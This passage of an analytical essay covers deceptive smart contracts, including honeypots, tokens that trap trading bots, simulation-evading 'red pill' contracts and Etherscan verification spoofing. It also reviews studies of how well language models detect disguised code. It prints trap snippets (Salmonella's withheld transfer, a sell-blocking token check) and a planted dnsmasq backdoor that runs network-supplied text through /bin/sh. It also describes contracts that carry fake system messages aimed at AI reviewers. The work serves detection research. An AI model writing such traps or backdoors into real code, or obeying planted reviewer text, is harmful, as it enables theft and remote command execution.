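The Solidity team could treat a successful contest entry as a bug report. Reitwiessner wrote that the compiler could block Forster's trick by rejecting changes of text direction that continue past the end of a comment, and linked to an entry in Solidity's issue tracker. Some entries also became teaching material. *ConsenSys CTF Writeup*, by the security researcher samczsun, refers readers to one that explains how an array that is too long can let an attacker write anywhere in a contract's storage. Solidity 0.6.0 later stopped programmers from setting an array's length directly, to prevent gigantic arrays from overlapping other data.

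Solidity 0.5.0 also included two changes that directly stop some of the eight honeypot techniques. The compiler no longer accepts `var`, which gave For_Test its undersized counter, and it rejects records without their own place in storage, which GuessNumber needed to overwrite its secret number. By 2019, Camino and colleagues described the skipping of empty text as a former compiler bug.

Solidity took longer to restrict reused names. Older versions even let a program redefine built-in names such as `now`, as Secureum's *3.17 Shadowing & Pre-declaration* explains. Version 0.6.0 rejects a contract that declares a variable with the same name as one it inherits, which is what KingOfTheHill did with `owner`. But Solidity's description of the change says the ban applies only if the inherited variable is visible to the new contract. A swindler could still have two variables named `owner` by marking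 the inherited one `private`, which many readers would take as a sign of caution.

A swindler can also keep using an old compiler, and contracts already on the blockchain remain in use. All but one of the honeypots in Camino and colleagues' data were compiled with a version from the 0.4 series. The new compiler rules still help readers, because an outdated compiler version in a new contract is now a reason for suspicion. The rules of the 2017 contest had already stated that asking for a particular version would raise "major red flags" with the judges.

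Banning one construct can leave a similar one available. In version 0.8, ordinary arithmetic stops with an error if a result doesn't fit its type. With this check, Moore's formula would fail instead of producing an enormous number, which would prevent the theft but also keep the owner from withdrawing anything. The check doesn't cover operations that shift a number's binary digits, and William Bowling used one in an entry that earned an honorable mention in 2022. The judges thought it would make readers suspicious because such operations are rare.

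The next contest, in 2024, drew eight submissions, down from 18 in 2022, and only four qualified (Mehta, 2024, *Announcing the Winners of the Underhanded Solidity Contest 2024*). The theme was a new form of temporary storage, and few entries contained a bug that depended on it. One judge took the low turnout as a sign that the compiler had matured. Another asked whether the feature was safe or whether developers had kept their best ideas to themselves. The theme may also have discouraged entrants because it required low-level code.

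### What Etherscan's check mark covers

Compiler changes can't do much about the other four techniques. Balance disorder depends on the virtual machine, so it works the same in any version of Solidity. The remaining three exploit what Etherscan displays. By the time Ferreira Torres and colleagues published in 2019, Etherscan had stopped hiding the ends of long lines, but it still left out calls that carried no ether. It also still checked source code against bytecode one contract at a time, so a verified contract could call a straw man in place of the contract shown in its source.

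*Hiding in Plain Sight* (samczsun, 2022), written by a judge of that year's contest, explains how to make Etherscan approve source code for a contract that does something else. The compiler adds a short block of information to the end of the bytecode, including a hash of details of the compilation. Harmless differences can change that hash, so Etherscan looked for the marker in front of it and ignored the bytes that followed.

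Samczsun wrote source code containing two large constants that, once compiled, looked like the beginning and end of such a block. Etherscan also ignored the bytes between them, although they were part of the running program. Samczsun replaced those bytes with different instructions, and Etherscan still marked the contract as verified. The gap held only 31 bytes, too few for the intended backdoor, so Samczsun put the rest in the real block at the end.

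The contract was a puzzle for a hacking competition, and the backdoor gave extra points to players who found it. But a swindler could have used the same method to publish harmless source code for a fraudulent contract. Neither a reader nor a tool that analyzed only the source code could have found the fraud, but a tool like HoneyBadger would at least have examined the bytecode that runs.

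## Contracts that trap trading bots and transaction simulators, 2021 to 2026

The Ethereum honeypots of 2017 and 2018 caught people who read code. Since 2021, people have written contracts that mislead trading programs that never read a contract's code. Many programs on Ethereum trade this way, either by calculating what a trade should earn or by running the trade on a copy of the blockchain and checking the result.

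### Poisoning sandwich traders

On Uniswap, the largest decentralized exchange on Ethereum, people trade with a pool that holds two assets. Apart from fees, the product of the two amounts stays the same, which sets the price. Suppose a pool holds 100 ether and 10,000 tokens, and a customer orders tokens for 10 ether. The customer should get 909 tokens. But a bot can often see the order before it goes into a block and buy first. The bot buys 909 tokens for 10 ether, which raises the price. The customer now gets only 758 tokens and raises the price further. The bot then sells its 909 tokens for 11.8 ether, a profit of 1.8 ether before fees. Traders call this a sandwich because the bot's two trades surround the customer's.

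The main risk used to be that only one of the bot's trades would go through. By early 2021, traders could submit all three transactions as a bundle that executed completely or not at all. Some began to call the profits risk-free, but they still depended on how the token behaved.

On March 19, 2021, according to CoinDesk (2021), the bot trader Nathan Worsley released two tokens, Salmonella and Listeria, to trap sandwich bots. This is the central part of Salmonella, slightly simplified:

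```solidity
_balances[sender] -= amount;
if (sender == ownerA || sender == ownerB) {
    _balances[recipient] += amount;
} else {
    uint256 trapAmount = (amount * 10) / 100;
    _balances[recipient] += trapAmount;
}
emit Transfer(sender, recipient, amount);
```

When someone buys the token, the sender is the pool, so the buyer receives only a tenth of the amount, but the last line records the full amount in the public log. Worsley set up a pool and sent it orders that looked worth sandwiching. A bot that paid 10 ether in the example above would have received 91 tokens instead of 909, and the token would have withheld nine tenths again when the bot tried to sell.

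The bots calculated the pool's prices correctly but assumed that the token would deliver what the pool sent. The mining pool Ethermine, which ran the busiest sandwich bot at the time, lost about 103 ether within hours, and about 17 other bots lost smaller sums. CoinDesk put the total at 130 ether, or about $250,000. The takings soon fell as the bots' operators adjusted their checks. Worsley didn't need to disguise the code, which has a variable named `trapAmount`, because no person would read it before the bots traded.

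One remedy is to compare the buyer's token balance before and after the purchase. Uniswap has a purchase function that does this, and according to dmarzzz's *undercooked*, it "essentially patched" Salmonella. But the token's own code also reports the balance, and *Why Trick Me* (Gan, Wang and Lin, 2023) warns that a malicious token can falsify both its log and its balances. The paper's test therefore also sells the token and measures how much of the other, valuable asset comes back.

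### Contracts that recognize a simulation

Bots and wallets simulate transactions before sending them, because a trader who checks the balance after a real purchase may already have lost the money. When a website asks a wallet's owner to sign a call to an unfamiliar contract, the wallet first runs the call on a copy of the blockchain's current state and shows what the owner would pay and receive. This automates the trial run that Murdoch and Paterno taught developers to do by hand.

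In 2023, the wallet company Zengo disclosed a way to defeat these simulations. Zengo's *Security vulnerability in popular web3 transaction simulation solutions* explains that a contract can read details of the block it is running in, such as the address of the block's producer. A simulation has no real block, so some simulators used a placeholder address of all zeros. A contract can therefore pay the user generously when it finds the zeros and keep the user's money when it finds a real address. Zengo called this a red pill attack, after the pill in the film *The Matrix* that reveals to the hero that his world is a simulation.

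In Zengo's demonstration, the Coinbase wallet predicted that a payment worth about 10 cents would bring in about $30, but the real transaction brought in nothing. Zengo remarked that users would have been better off without the simulation, since the false result helped persuade them to pay. Volkswagen's software and the TestToken honeypot also behaved well when they detected a test, but in this case the test result itself was used to lure the user.

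Almost every simulator Zengo inspected had some version of the flaw. TechTarget's *ZenGo finds transaction simulation flaw in Coinbase others* lists the Rabby wallet and the security tools Blowfish, Pocket Universe and Fire among those affected. Most vendors quickly fixed it by supplying realistic values, such as the address of the previous block's producer. Zengo had found no evidence that thieves were using the method, although one person claimed they might have seen it.

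A trial run is evidence about the real run only if the program can't detect which one it is in. The tester has to reproduce every fact that the program can look up, because the program's author can use any discrepancy to make it behave differently in the test. Zengo later published a contract that wallet developers can use to test their simulators for known differences. Simulating an opponent in an open-source game is easier if the rules let programs read only each other's text, because then no clock or block number can reveal the simulation.

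### Changing the contract after the check

A thief can defeat a transaction simulation without detecting it, by changing the contract's stored data after the simulation runs. Scam Sniffer's *Transaction Simulation Spoofing* describes a theft of 143.45 ether, about $461,000, that became public in January 2025. A fraudulent website invited the victim to claim some ether, and the wallet's simulation accurately showed a tiny payment coming in. The thieves then changed the data stored in the contract. About 30 seconds later the victim signed, and the same call emptied the wallet.

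This kind of theft seems to have been rare at the time. CryptoSlate's *Crypto phishing scams drained $10.25 million in January* (2025) gives Scam Sniffer's total for simulation spoofing that month as $471,000, and this one theft must account for nearly all of it. Scam Sniffer suggested that wallets repeat the simulation just before signing, display its age and warn about old results. Zengo's *Web3 Transaction Simulation White Paper* (2025) lists the gap between simulation and execution among the basic limits of simulation. Repeating the simulation shortens the gap but can't eliminate it, because the thief may still get a change into the same block as the victim's transaction.

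In June 2026, an attacker trapped jaredfromsubway.eth, one of Ethereum's most active sandwich bots. The attack relied on token approvals. A trader has to approve an amount before a contract can take tokens as payment, and whatever the contract doesn't take stays approved until the trader cancels it.

CertiK's *JaredFromSubway MEV bot Incident Analysis* (2026) reports that the attacker published 131 bait tokens, many of them posing as versions of WETH, a token that represents ether. The bait tokens' contracts offered one bait token for each real one, and rigged pools made the exchange look profitable. In the first trade, the bot approved a payment, the contract took it, and the bot made a profit of about 0.002 WETH.

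The contracts behaved normally for nearly a day. Then the attacker began marking individual blocks. In a marked block, the contracts still issued their tokens but didn't collect the payment, so the approval remained open. The attacker paid to have the marks recorded just ahead of the bot's trades. The Block's *Notorious 'jaredfromsubway' MEV bot drained for roughly $7.5 million in counter-MEV honeypot* (2026) summarizes an analysis by the pseudonymous developer banteg, who found that the contracts behaved normally in small batches of trades and left approvals open in large ones. According to Blockaid's *The Predator Becomes the Prey* (2026), the approvals grew from about 0.007 WETH to about 92 WETH per contract. Less than an hour after the first marked block, the attacker used the open approvals to take about $7.5 million in a single transaction.

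A simulation based on the previous block would probably have missed the attacker's mark. But even a perfect simulation of each trade would have shown a profit, because the theft happened in a later transaction. The bot should have checked which permissions each trade left in place and canceled them.

### Tokens that buyers can't sell

Anyone can create a token and open a Uniswap pool for it. The token standard prescribes the names of the functions that move tokens but not what those functions do, so the author of a token can let people buy it and stop them from selling. Huynh, Dau and colleagues (2023), in *From Programming Bugs to Multimillion-Dollar Scams*, call these trapdoor tokens. They distinguish them from honeypot contracts because the victims are usually novices or bots that can't judge the code, and they aren't trying to rob anyone. A simple example is AquaDrops, shortened here:

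```solidity
function _beforeTokenTransfer(address from, address to) internal {
    if (to == uniswapV2Pair)
        require(_enable[from], "something went wrong");
}
```

A holder sells by sending tokens to the pool, here called `uniswapV2Pair`. For such transfers, the function requires the seller to be on the list `_enable`, which contains only the creator.

Other tokens hide the trap better. ELONAJA has a list named `_isBot`, supposedly to keep out automated traders. Its creator added bots to the list, but also added the token contract's own address. An ordinary seller isn't on the list and passes the check, but during the sale the contract tries to destroy some of its own tokens by calling the same transfer function with itself as the sender. That second call fails the check and cancels the sale. To spot the trap, a reader would have to find the contract's address in a list of bots and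 notice that the transfer function calls itself.

The creator of the CPP4U token secretly raised the selling fee to 1,000%. Subtracting the fee from the sale amount then gave a negative number, which the variable couldn't hold, so each sale failed with an arithmetic error that looked like an honest bug. The Underhanded C Contest rewarded the same kind of excuse.

Names also misled GoPlus, a commercial detection tool. It missed a token whose list of permitted sellers was named `allow`, which resembles the name of a standard feature. Huynh and colleagues wrote a tool that ignores names and follows how the code uses each variable. They compared the two tools on 290 tokens that they had labeled by hand. Of the 182 tokens with a switch for suspending trading, GoPlus recognized the switch in 107 and their tool recognized it in 178. The researchers built one of the tools and labeled the tokens themselves,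 which could have biased the comparison, but the gap is large.

Estimates of how common unsellable tokens are depend heavily on the definition. Huynh and colleagues confirmed that 11,943 (9%) of the 131,172 tokens on Uniswap V2 up to January 2023 were unsellable. This figure is cautious because they counted a token only if a test sale failed and its published source code explained why. Gan and colleagues flagged 84% of 10,000 randomly chosen pools, but their method can't distinguish a trap from a legitimate power to block certain accounts. *A Sea of Coins* (Naviglio, Tarantelli and Lillo, 2025) reports a figure of 88% for the 17,194 tokens launched on Uniswap V2 in eight weeks of late 2024. It counts a token if either of two commercial tools ever flagged it, which probably makes the figure too high.

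Even 9% is far more than the 0.3% of contracts that HoneyBadger flagged as honeypots, so a detection tool for new tokens can produce more false alarms and still be useful.

### How long a trial has to last

Swindlers also recruit buyers directly. In *Pump-and-Dump meets Honeypot Tokens*, Cernera, La Morgia and colleagues (2026) examined 3,677 occasions from 2021 to 2025 on which Telegram channels told subscribers to buy a token before its price rose. In 71.5% of cases the token was a trap. The organizers made money from 99.3% of these traps and earned more than $7 million in total, far more than the creators of the early honeypots did.

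One of the traps was a token named VAULT. Its contract delivered tokens only to a list of accounts belonging to the creator and four accomplices. Before the announcement, the creator bought and sold small amounts 30 times so that the token would look easy to trade to anyone who checked past sales. Thirty-three subscribers then paid about $1,600 and received nothing, while the accomplices' purchases drove the price up. Afterward the channel posted a chart showing a rise of 2,000%. Across all the traps, known accomplices accounted for about 93% of the value sold.

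Cernera and colleagues tested the tokens with HoneyCheck, a program that copies the blockchain as it was when the announcement appeared, then buys the token and tries to sell it. When HoneyCheck sold immediately, 1,095 of the 2,121 tokens blocked the sale. Another 191 allowed an immediate sale but blocked one made up to ten seconds later. Waiting as long as ten minutes exposed no more traps. Another 206 tokens let the trades go through but took more than 90% of the proceeds. The 191 delayed traps exploit testers' habit of selling right after buying, whereas a person normally waits for the price to rise.

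HoneyCheck flagged 90% of the 1,859 tokens that Huynh and colleagues had identified by hand, and none of 967 tokens from a list approved by the exchange PancakeSwap. The second result probably overstates the tool's accuracy, because established tokens are easier to clear than new and obscure ones.

Some of the tokens HoneyCheck missed had a trap that their owner never activated. Others let everyone sell at first, and the owner then blocked each buyer after the purchase. A new buyer can't detect this by simulating a trade, however realistic the simulation, because the owner decides later whether to block them. Gan and colleagues instead simulated sales from the accounts of people who had already bought the token, and also watched for balances that disappeared after a purchase. These checks work only after the trap has caught someone.

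### Trading bots that rob their owners

By early 2024, scammers were also targeting people who wanted their own trading bot. SentinelLABS's *Smart Contract Scams* describes YouTube videos that offered free code for a supposedly profitable Ethereum bot. Viewers copied the code into an online programming tool, deployed it to the blockchain and sent it at least half an ether. They then called a function named `Start`, which was supposed to begin trading but sent the money to the scammer. If a victim never called it, the scammer could still withdraw the money.

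The contracts all hide the swindler's address. Some store it as a long decimal number or in fragments. Others calculate it from two constants with names like `DexRouter` and `factory`, using a bitwise operation so that neither constant resembles the result. A Solidity expert would wonder why a trading bot needed to calculate an address this way, but the videos appealed to people who couldn't read the code. The victims published the contract from their own accounts, which may have made the program feel like theirs.

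The comments under the videos were overwhelmingly positive, and SentinelLABS thinks the scammers were deleting the rest. The most successful video had more than 387,000 views, and the address in its code received 244.9 ether, about $902,000. Two other addresses received about $28,000 and $15,000. Nothing in SentinelLABS's description suggests that these contracts could detect a test, so running them first on a private copy of the blockchain would probably have shown the money leaving.

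### AI agents

As of early December 2026, no documented case was known of an AI agent losing money to a disguised contract while trading, or approving one while auditing it. CertiK and Blockaid describe jaredfromsubway.eth as an automated program that looks for profitable trades, not as an AI agent. The best-known loss by an AI trading agent that year resulted from a mistake. Finance Magnates' *AI Crypto Bot “Accidentally” Drops 52 Million Memecoin, Flooding an X Wallet* reports that an agent named Lobstar Wilde meant to give a stranger about 52,000 tokens but sent about 52 million, worth roughly $250,000 on paper. *A Gingerbread House for LLM Agents* (2026) covers honeypots for AI agents, but these are decoys that lure autonomous attackers into an isolated environment.

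The lack of known cases is only weak evidence that AI agents can avoid such traps. The agents' owners have little reason to publicize losses, and the blockchain doesn't record whether a person, a simple bot or a language model decided to make a trade.

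## Language models as readers of disguised code, 2023 to 2026

In 2025 and 2026, several teams tested how well language models see through disguised code by giving them programs with known traps and checking whether they found the traps. Known losses provide little evidence of this ability. The teams' results look quite different from those on accidental flaws, which language models now find in large numbers. In *The Deception Delta*, Schefold (2026) explains that a vulnerability is a defect, while a deceptive contract works as its author intended and hides its purpose from whoever analyzes it.

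Most of the models in these tests came out before the spring of 2026, and AI has improved quickly since, so the figures are better evidence of which disguises are hard to detect than of what the best current model would miss.

### Backdoors in compiled programs

The best-known test is BinaryAudit, from the software company Quesma. For *We hid backdoors in ~40 MB binaries and asked AI + Ghidra*, Grabowski, Strzaliński and colleagues (2026) planted backdoors in four open-source network programs: a web server, an SSH server, a load balancer and dnsmasq, which assigns addresses to the devices on a network. They gave AI agents only the compiled files, along with free tools for analyzing machine code. These included Ghidra, which translates machine code back into rough C, usually without the names that made the original readable.

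In most tasks the agent had to decide whether a file contained a backdoor and give the address of the function that held it, so correctly guessing "yes" wasn't enough. In a few tasks it received three files and had to pick out the altered ones. These were no easier, although the team had expected them to be.

Claude Opus 4.6 did best, solving 49% of the tasks. Gemini 3 Pro solved 44% and Claude Opus 4.5 solved 37%. The models also reported nonexistent problems in clean files 28% of the time. These results are weak given that the backdoors weren't well disguised. Grabowski and his colleagues thought a skilled human analyst could spot them relatively easily.

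In one successful attempt, Claude Opus 4.5 found a backdoor in the web server in five minutes. The backdoor ran any command sent in an undocumented header. The model first searched the files for suspicious words and found nothing. It then listed the system functions used by each of the program's 26 libraries and saw that one library used `popen`, which runs commands. It traced the call to a function still labeled `li_check_debug_header`. The label helped a great deal because a function that checks a header has no obvious reason to run commands.

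The most instructive failure involved seven lines in dnsmasq, shortened here:

```c
if (opt = option_find(mess, sz, 224, 1)) {
    /* copy the option's contents into buf */
    execl("/bin/sh", "sh", "-c", buf, NULL);
}
```

Devices send messages with numbered options to dnsmasq. Option 224 was invented for the test, and dnsmasq runs whatever command it contains. Claude Opus 4.6 found the function and the `execl` call. But dnsmasq also has a legitimate feature that runs a script when it assigns an address, and the model concluded that the call was probably part of that feature and moved on without checking where the command came from.

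Nobody had written an innocent explanation for this backdoor, but the model supplied one from its general knowledge of dnsmasq. The human analysts Dawu and 0x7F also seem to have stopped at the first explanation that fit when they explained a honeypot's bait without mentioning its trap.

False alarms could be just as convincing. Gemini 3 Pro reported that one server treated a storage-time setting as text and ran it as a command. The report included the setting's number and its position in memory, but the server's code reads the setting as a number and never runs it.

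### Later models on BinaryAudit

In late November 2026, the top score was still 49%. Quesma's *Can AI find backdoors in raw machine code?* ranks 26 models on 33 tasks, with these results among them:

| Model | Backdoors found | False positive rate |
|---|---|---|
| Gemini 3.1 Pro preview | 49% | 17% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 49% | not in the summary table |
| GPT-5.2-Codex, highest reasoning setting | 46% | 0% |
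| GPT-5.4, highest reasoning setting | 18% | not in the summary table |
| GPT-5.2-Codex, standard setting | 9% | not in the summary table |

GPT-5.2-Codex found about five times as many backdoors at its highest reasoning setting as at its standard one, so a score for the model means little without the setting. It found 46% of the backdoors with no false alarms, which is arguably the best result in the table.

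A model can also have a low false positive rate because it rarely reports backdoors. Quesma's *BinaryAudit/gpt-5.4-high* (2026) gives that model an overall pass rate of 49%, but this covers all 33 tasks, including tool-use exercises and files with no backdoor. The model passed all eight clean-file tasks listed there, as would a reviewer who approved everything, but it found only 14% of the backdoors.

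The 0% for GPT-5.2-Codex is also imprecise, because with about three runs per task and so few clean files, the test can't distinguish a true rate of zero from one of a few percent. The newest model with a release date is GPT-5.4, from March 2026, so the unchanged top score doesn't show how the stronger models released since would perform.

### Contracts that hide a theft

Schefold, who works for the state criminal police in Baden-Württemberg, Germany, tested models on a problem that financial investigators face. A suspicious contract is on the blockchain, nobody has published its source code, and the investigator asks a language model what the bytecode does. The test used 13 purpose-built contracts. Nine concealed a way for a privileged account to take the deposits, two contained such a theft without disguise, and two were honest. (The disguised contracts rob ordinary depositors, so they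 aren't honeypots of the kind HoneyBadger looks for.)

Twenty-two models from seven providers each read every contract five times under each of six prompts, without tools or follow-up questions. They identified the theft in 41% of readings when it was undisguised and in 21% when it was disguised. Claude Opus with extended reasoning did best, identifying the theft in 76% of disguised contracts, while most models found it in fewer than 15%. Schefold had developed the disguises by testing them against Opus.

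The most effective disguises contained nothing false. One contract splits the theft across five functions that each perform an innocent-looking step, and the models caught it in 3.5% of readings. Another omits the numeric code that identifies the transfer function and instead computes it from two stored numbers when the contract runs. The models caught it in 2.3% of readings.

Surprisingly, false documentation helped models find the theft. Schefold took the five-function contract and added about four kilobytes of text, including a forged audit report that described the theft as a normal accounting method. The share of readings that identified the mechanism rose from 3.5% to 49%, because the models learned from the forged report what to look for. But a reading counted as a detection if the model described the theft correctly, even if it then called it harmless. The models called the theft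 harmless in 63% of detections, so only about 18% of all readings gave a correct warning. The strongest models improved most. Claude Opus without extended reasoning went from missing the theft in most readings to warning about it in nearly all of them, a gain of 90 percentage points.

Two contracts contained text addressed to the model, such as a fake system message saying that the Ethereum Foundation had verified the contract. The model detected the planted text in 44.5% of the readings in which it missed the theft. Telling models in advance to ignore embedded instructions made almost no difference on average.

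Schefold built an honest control contract to match the one with the forged audit. It has the same general design and the same owner-only function, but a harmless calculation in place of the theft. Models wrongly reported a theft in 6.8% of readings of the control. When Schefold counted only whether the model gave a risk rating of at least 3 out of 5, the results were nearly identical, at 69.2% for the thieving contract and 69.3% for the honest one. A high risk rating therefore doesn't show that a model has found the theft, so the test has to ask for the mechanism.

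Detection rose from 41.7% with bytecode to 97.9% with source code on a smaller set of eight contracts and eight models. The models raised one false alarm in 40 readings of the honest twin. This is the most encouraging result for models as reviewers, but Schefold had designed the contracts to mislead readers of bytecode. Entrants in the Underhanded Solidity Contest put all their effort into misleading readers of the source. The result therefore shows that models can follow a theft through readable code, but not whether they would notice that `indexed` values are evaluated from right to left.

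Other language models graded most of the answers, which adds some uncertainty. Schefold checked the graders against 50 answers labeled by one human expert. Disguise also reduced detection on two measures that didn't depend on the graders, though by less.

Honeypots of the older kind are largely missing from this research. Schefold found that nearly all evaluations of language models on smart contracts use known classes of accidental flaws. This gap matters for AI agents that search for contracts to exploit, because honeypots are meant to attract such readers. A benchmark that rewards agents for the ether they extract could include a few honeypots and subtract the ether that agents lose to them.

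### Tokens that trap their buyers

*TrapHunter* (Wu, Liu and colleagues, 2026) gave language models more help by tracing each path through a contract's source code and recording when one function reads a value that another can change. The tool looks for unsellable tokens and related traps, such as a hidden way for the creator to raise fees or create unlimited new tokens. In a token called BitDao, for example, the check that can block a transfer reads a value that `decreaseAllowance` can switch. A function with that name usually just lowers a spending permission, so a person reading the transfer code would have little reason to look there.

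The tool compares these paths with a standard token, prompts a model three times to classify each difference as a trap or not, and takes the majority answer. It then tries to trigger the suspected trap on a copy of the blockchain.

The researchers tested the tool with DeepSeek-V3, GPT-5 and Gemini 2.5 Pro on 269 known malicious contracts containing 501 labeled traps. The average detection rate was 85.4% and the average precision was 81.8%. This set contained no honest contracts, so the precision mostly reflects whether the tool named the right kind of trap. A second test, on 48 newly published Ethereum contracts, better measures false alarms. With GPT-5, the tool found all 25 contracts that contained traps and wrongly flagged 6 of the other 23, a false positive rate of 26%. Legitimate transaction fees caused many of its errors.

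The researchers also removed parts of the tool to see what each contributed. Without the language model, almost every alarm was correct, but the tool found only half the traps. Without the traced connections between functions, the model found 65% of the traps instead of 87% and raised far more false alarms. The model is evidently good at judging the purpose of a suspicious path once another program has found it. But GPT-5 was slow, taking more than 14 minutes per contract on average.

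### Malicious packages

Programmers download packages from public registries, such as npm for JavaScript and PyPI for Python, and criminals upload packages that steal passwords or other data. Malicious packages provide much larger samples than smart contracts do. Guo, Liu and colleagues (2026) tested 11 tools on 6,420 malicious package versions and 7,288 benign packages in *How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?*

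Two of the tools, SocketAI and IntelGuard, used the same language model, GPT-4.1 mini. SocketAI found 44% of the malicious packages and IntelGuard found 94%, and about 98% of each tool's alarms were correct. SocketAI prompts the model to judge the code and then to challenge its own conclusions, which often led it to reverse a correct finding that the code was malicious. It also reads at most 20 files per package. IntelGuard first retrieves similar examples from a collection based on more than 8,000 reports of earlier attacks, then prompts the model to compare them with the code.

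The comparison shows that crediting or blaming the model alone can be misleading. It is less useful for judging how models handle disguises, because 80.3% of the malicious packages made no attempt to evade detection. GuardDog, which uses fixed rules and no language model, found 90%. Packages that check their environment before acting were among the hardest to detect, and the tools caught about half of them or fewer on average.

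*An Evaluation of Large Language Models for Detection of Malicious Python Packages* (Ryan, Khalil and colleagues, 2026) tested 13 models with several prompts and settings on a small sample of 103 files, one from each of 10 malicious and 93 benign packages. The models rarely missed the malicious files but often flagged benign ones. In 51% of the combinations of model, prompt and setting, fewer than half of the flagged files were malicious. The exception was GPT-4.1, which classified all 103 files correctly in eight of its ten combinations.

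The researchers then gave the models 370 malicious packages and asked which of 47 suspicious features each contained. The models often recognized commands that run other programs, but when a package's payload waited for a condition, they failed to mention this 77% of the time. That omission may not matter to someone deciding whether to install a package, since the package is malicious either way. But a player in a repeated game needs to know the condition, because it determines the round in which the opponent will defect.

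These are the results of the contract and package tests that included honest programs:

| Test | Reader | Harmful programs | Honest programs | Detection rate | False positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Schefold, bytecode | 22 models | 9 | 1 twin | 21% | 6.8% |
| Schefold, source code | 8 models | 6 | 1 twin | 97.9% | 2.5% |
| Wu and colleagues, new tokens | TrapHunter with GPT-5 | 25 | 23 | 100% | 26% |
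| Guo and colleagues | SocketAI with GPT-4.1 mini | 6,420 | 7,288 | 44% | 0.7% |
| Guo and colleagues | IntelGuard with GPT-4.1 mini | 6,420 | 7,288 | 94% | 1.5% |
| Guo and colleagues | GuardDog, no language model | 6,420 | 7,288 | 90% | 2.5% |
| Ryan and colleagues | GPT-4.1, best settings | 10 | 93 | 100% | 0% |

### How many false alarms are too many

The tolerable false positive rate depends on how many honest programs the reader has to check. *One Detector Fits All* (2025) describes a detector tuned for the maintainers of PyPI, with a target false positive rate of 0.1%. It checked 91,949 packages in 37 days, about 2,500 a day. On an average day it found two or three malicious packages and raised two false alarms, which a maintainer could review quickly.

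The same stream of packages would produce about 37 false alarms a day at IntelGuard's false positive rate of 1.5%, and about 700 at BinaryAudit's 28%. IntelGuard might do better in practice, because Guo and colleagues chose popular honest packages, which tend to set off more alarms. Grabowski and colleagues want a false positive rate below 0.001% for malware detection in general.

Some systems already come close to what a registry needs. *Cutting the Gordian Knot* (2026) reports a three-month trial of PyGuard, a language-model detector, on 8,249 new PyPI packages. PyGuard flagged 233, and PyPI's maintainers confirmed and removed 219 that the main public databases of malicious packages didn't list. Even if the other 14 were all false alarms, the false positive rate would be below 0.2%. The detection rate is unknown, since the trial doesn't establish how many of the roughly 8,000 unflagged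 packages were malicious. The disguises were mostly simple, since 94.4% of the malicious packages attacked as soon as someone installed them.

Lily, a tool that uses fuzzing instead of reading code as a person would, is a good comparison for language models that look for backdoors planted in otherwise honest source code. *Not In My Git Yard* (2026) tested Lily on 63 altered versions of open-source programs. Lily found the backdoor in 90% of runs when it checked a single change and in 83% when it checked a complete release, and it found every backdoor at least once in 20 runs. A language model that reviews source code should have to beat these results or catch what fuzzing misses, such as a trigger that random inputs would almost never hit.

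### A game of finding the difference

Most of these tests need a person or another model to decide whether an answer is right. Miceli Barone, Belle and Payani (2025), in *Program Semantic Inequivalence Game with Large Language Models*, devised a game that needs neither. One model, Alice, receives a program P and writes a variant Q, along with an input on which the two behave differently. A referee checks this by running both programs on that input. The other model, Bob, sees P and Q but not Alice's input, and wins if he finds any input on which the programs behave differently.

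The disguised tit-for-tat function would be a good move for Alice. Given the honest version, she could change `range(1, ROUNDS)` to `range(1, ROUNDS - 1)` and submit a record of nine cooperative moves as her proof. Bob would win by finding any nine-move record that ends in cooperation.

One of Alice's real variants comes from a program that finds the run of neighboring numbers with the largest sum and returns its length. This is its main part, slightly simplified:

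```python
for i in range(size):
    total += a[i]
    if best < total:
        best, start, end = total, s, i
    if total < 0:
        total = 0          # Alice removed this line
        s = i + 1
return end - start + 1
```

The missing line discards a running total once it becomes negative. A reader who compares the two versions will immediately see that the line is gone, but still has to work out when this changes the result. On the list 3, −5, 4, the original picks the 4 and the variant picks the 3, so both return 1, the length of the run they picked. On 3, −5, 2, 2, the original picks the last two numbers and returns 2. The variant carries the −2 forward, so its total never exceeds the initial 3 and it returns 1.

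Rice's theorem rules out a general method for proving that two programs behave the same, but a single input can prove that they differ. Anyone can check that input by running both programs. Bob wins by finding such an input, which is a short proof of defection of the kind CUPOD searches for. If he finds nothing, the programs may still differ. Alice could exploit this by writing a variant that misbehaves only if the input solves a cryptographic puzzle, much as the XZ backdoor responded only to the holder of a secret key. To discourage this, the researchers suggest rewarding Alice for moderately difficult variants.

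They also used the game to train the models, first Alice on the variants that fooled Bob at least half the time, then Bob on its own correct answers. With GPT-4o mini in both roles, Bob's success rate on variants of unfamiliar programs rose from 88.4% to 91.7%. Accuracy on other tasks barely improved, rising from 82.43% to 82.51% for recognizing security fixes in Python and from 55.23% to 55.60% for recognizing vulnerable C and C++ code. The models were small and Bob had only one round of training, so the experiment is a weak test of what the method could achieve.

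Asking the models to reason step by step lowered their accuracy on both security tasks. GPT-4o mini's accuracy on the Python fixes fell from 82% to 74%. The researchers suspect that longer reasoning gave the model more chances to abandon a correct first judgment, as Claude Opus 4.6 did with dnsmasq. But extended reasoning raised GPT-5.2's detection rate on Schefold's disguised contracts from 31% to 52%.

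They also tried a test from 2023 that resembles a contest trick. Each Python sample begins by exchanging the meanings of two standard functions:

```python
len, print = print, len
```

After this line, `len` prints and `print` measures length. The model sees an ordinary function and a copy with the two names exchanged throughout, and has to say which is more likely to be correct. The strange-looking copy is the right answer. In 2023, all the leading models did badly, and larger ones did worse. GPT-4o mini chose correctly only 1.65% of the time, where guessing would give 50%, so it was almost always following what the names usually mean. Training with the game raised this to 5.35%. GPT-4.1 nano didn't improve. (The researchers had first reported a gain for it, but they had trained that version with a faulty program for checking whether outputs differed.)

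Bob has an easier task than most reviewers because he knows that the programs differ and has the honest original. The game also contains no pairs that behave identically, so it cannot measure a false positive rate. Miceli Barone and colleagues describe later work in which one of them added pairs with formal proofs of equivalence. Those proofs accounted for most of the improvement in the models' reasoning, which suggests that a model learns more if it also has to recognize when two programs are equivalent.

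### When a model has read the answer

Experts wrote the entries to the Underhanded C Contest to deceive careful readers, which makes the programs promising material for testing language models. No such test appears to have been published. A simple one would prove little, because the contest's website prints many of the programs with explanations of their tricks. For example, it describes two warhead programs, by Sarah Newman and S. Gilles, that misbehave if someone changes the number of available processors. A model that had learned this page in training could give the right answer without analyzing the code.

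Researchers call this problem contamination. Renaming the variables doesn't solve it, because a model might still recognize a program that checks warheads and includes `math.h`. A better check is to repair the program and see whether the model's answer changes. In RHays's luggage program, changing the loop's limit from 5 to 4 makes the trap harmless. If a model still reported that a comment beginning with zero would hide the record, it would be repeating the published explanation.

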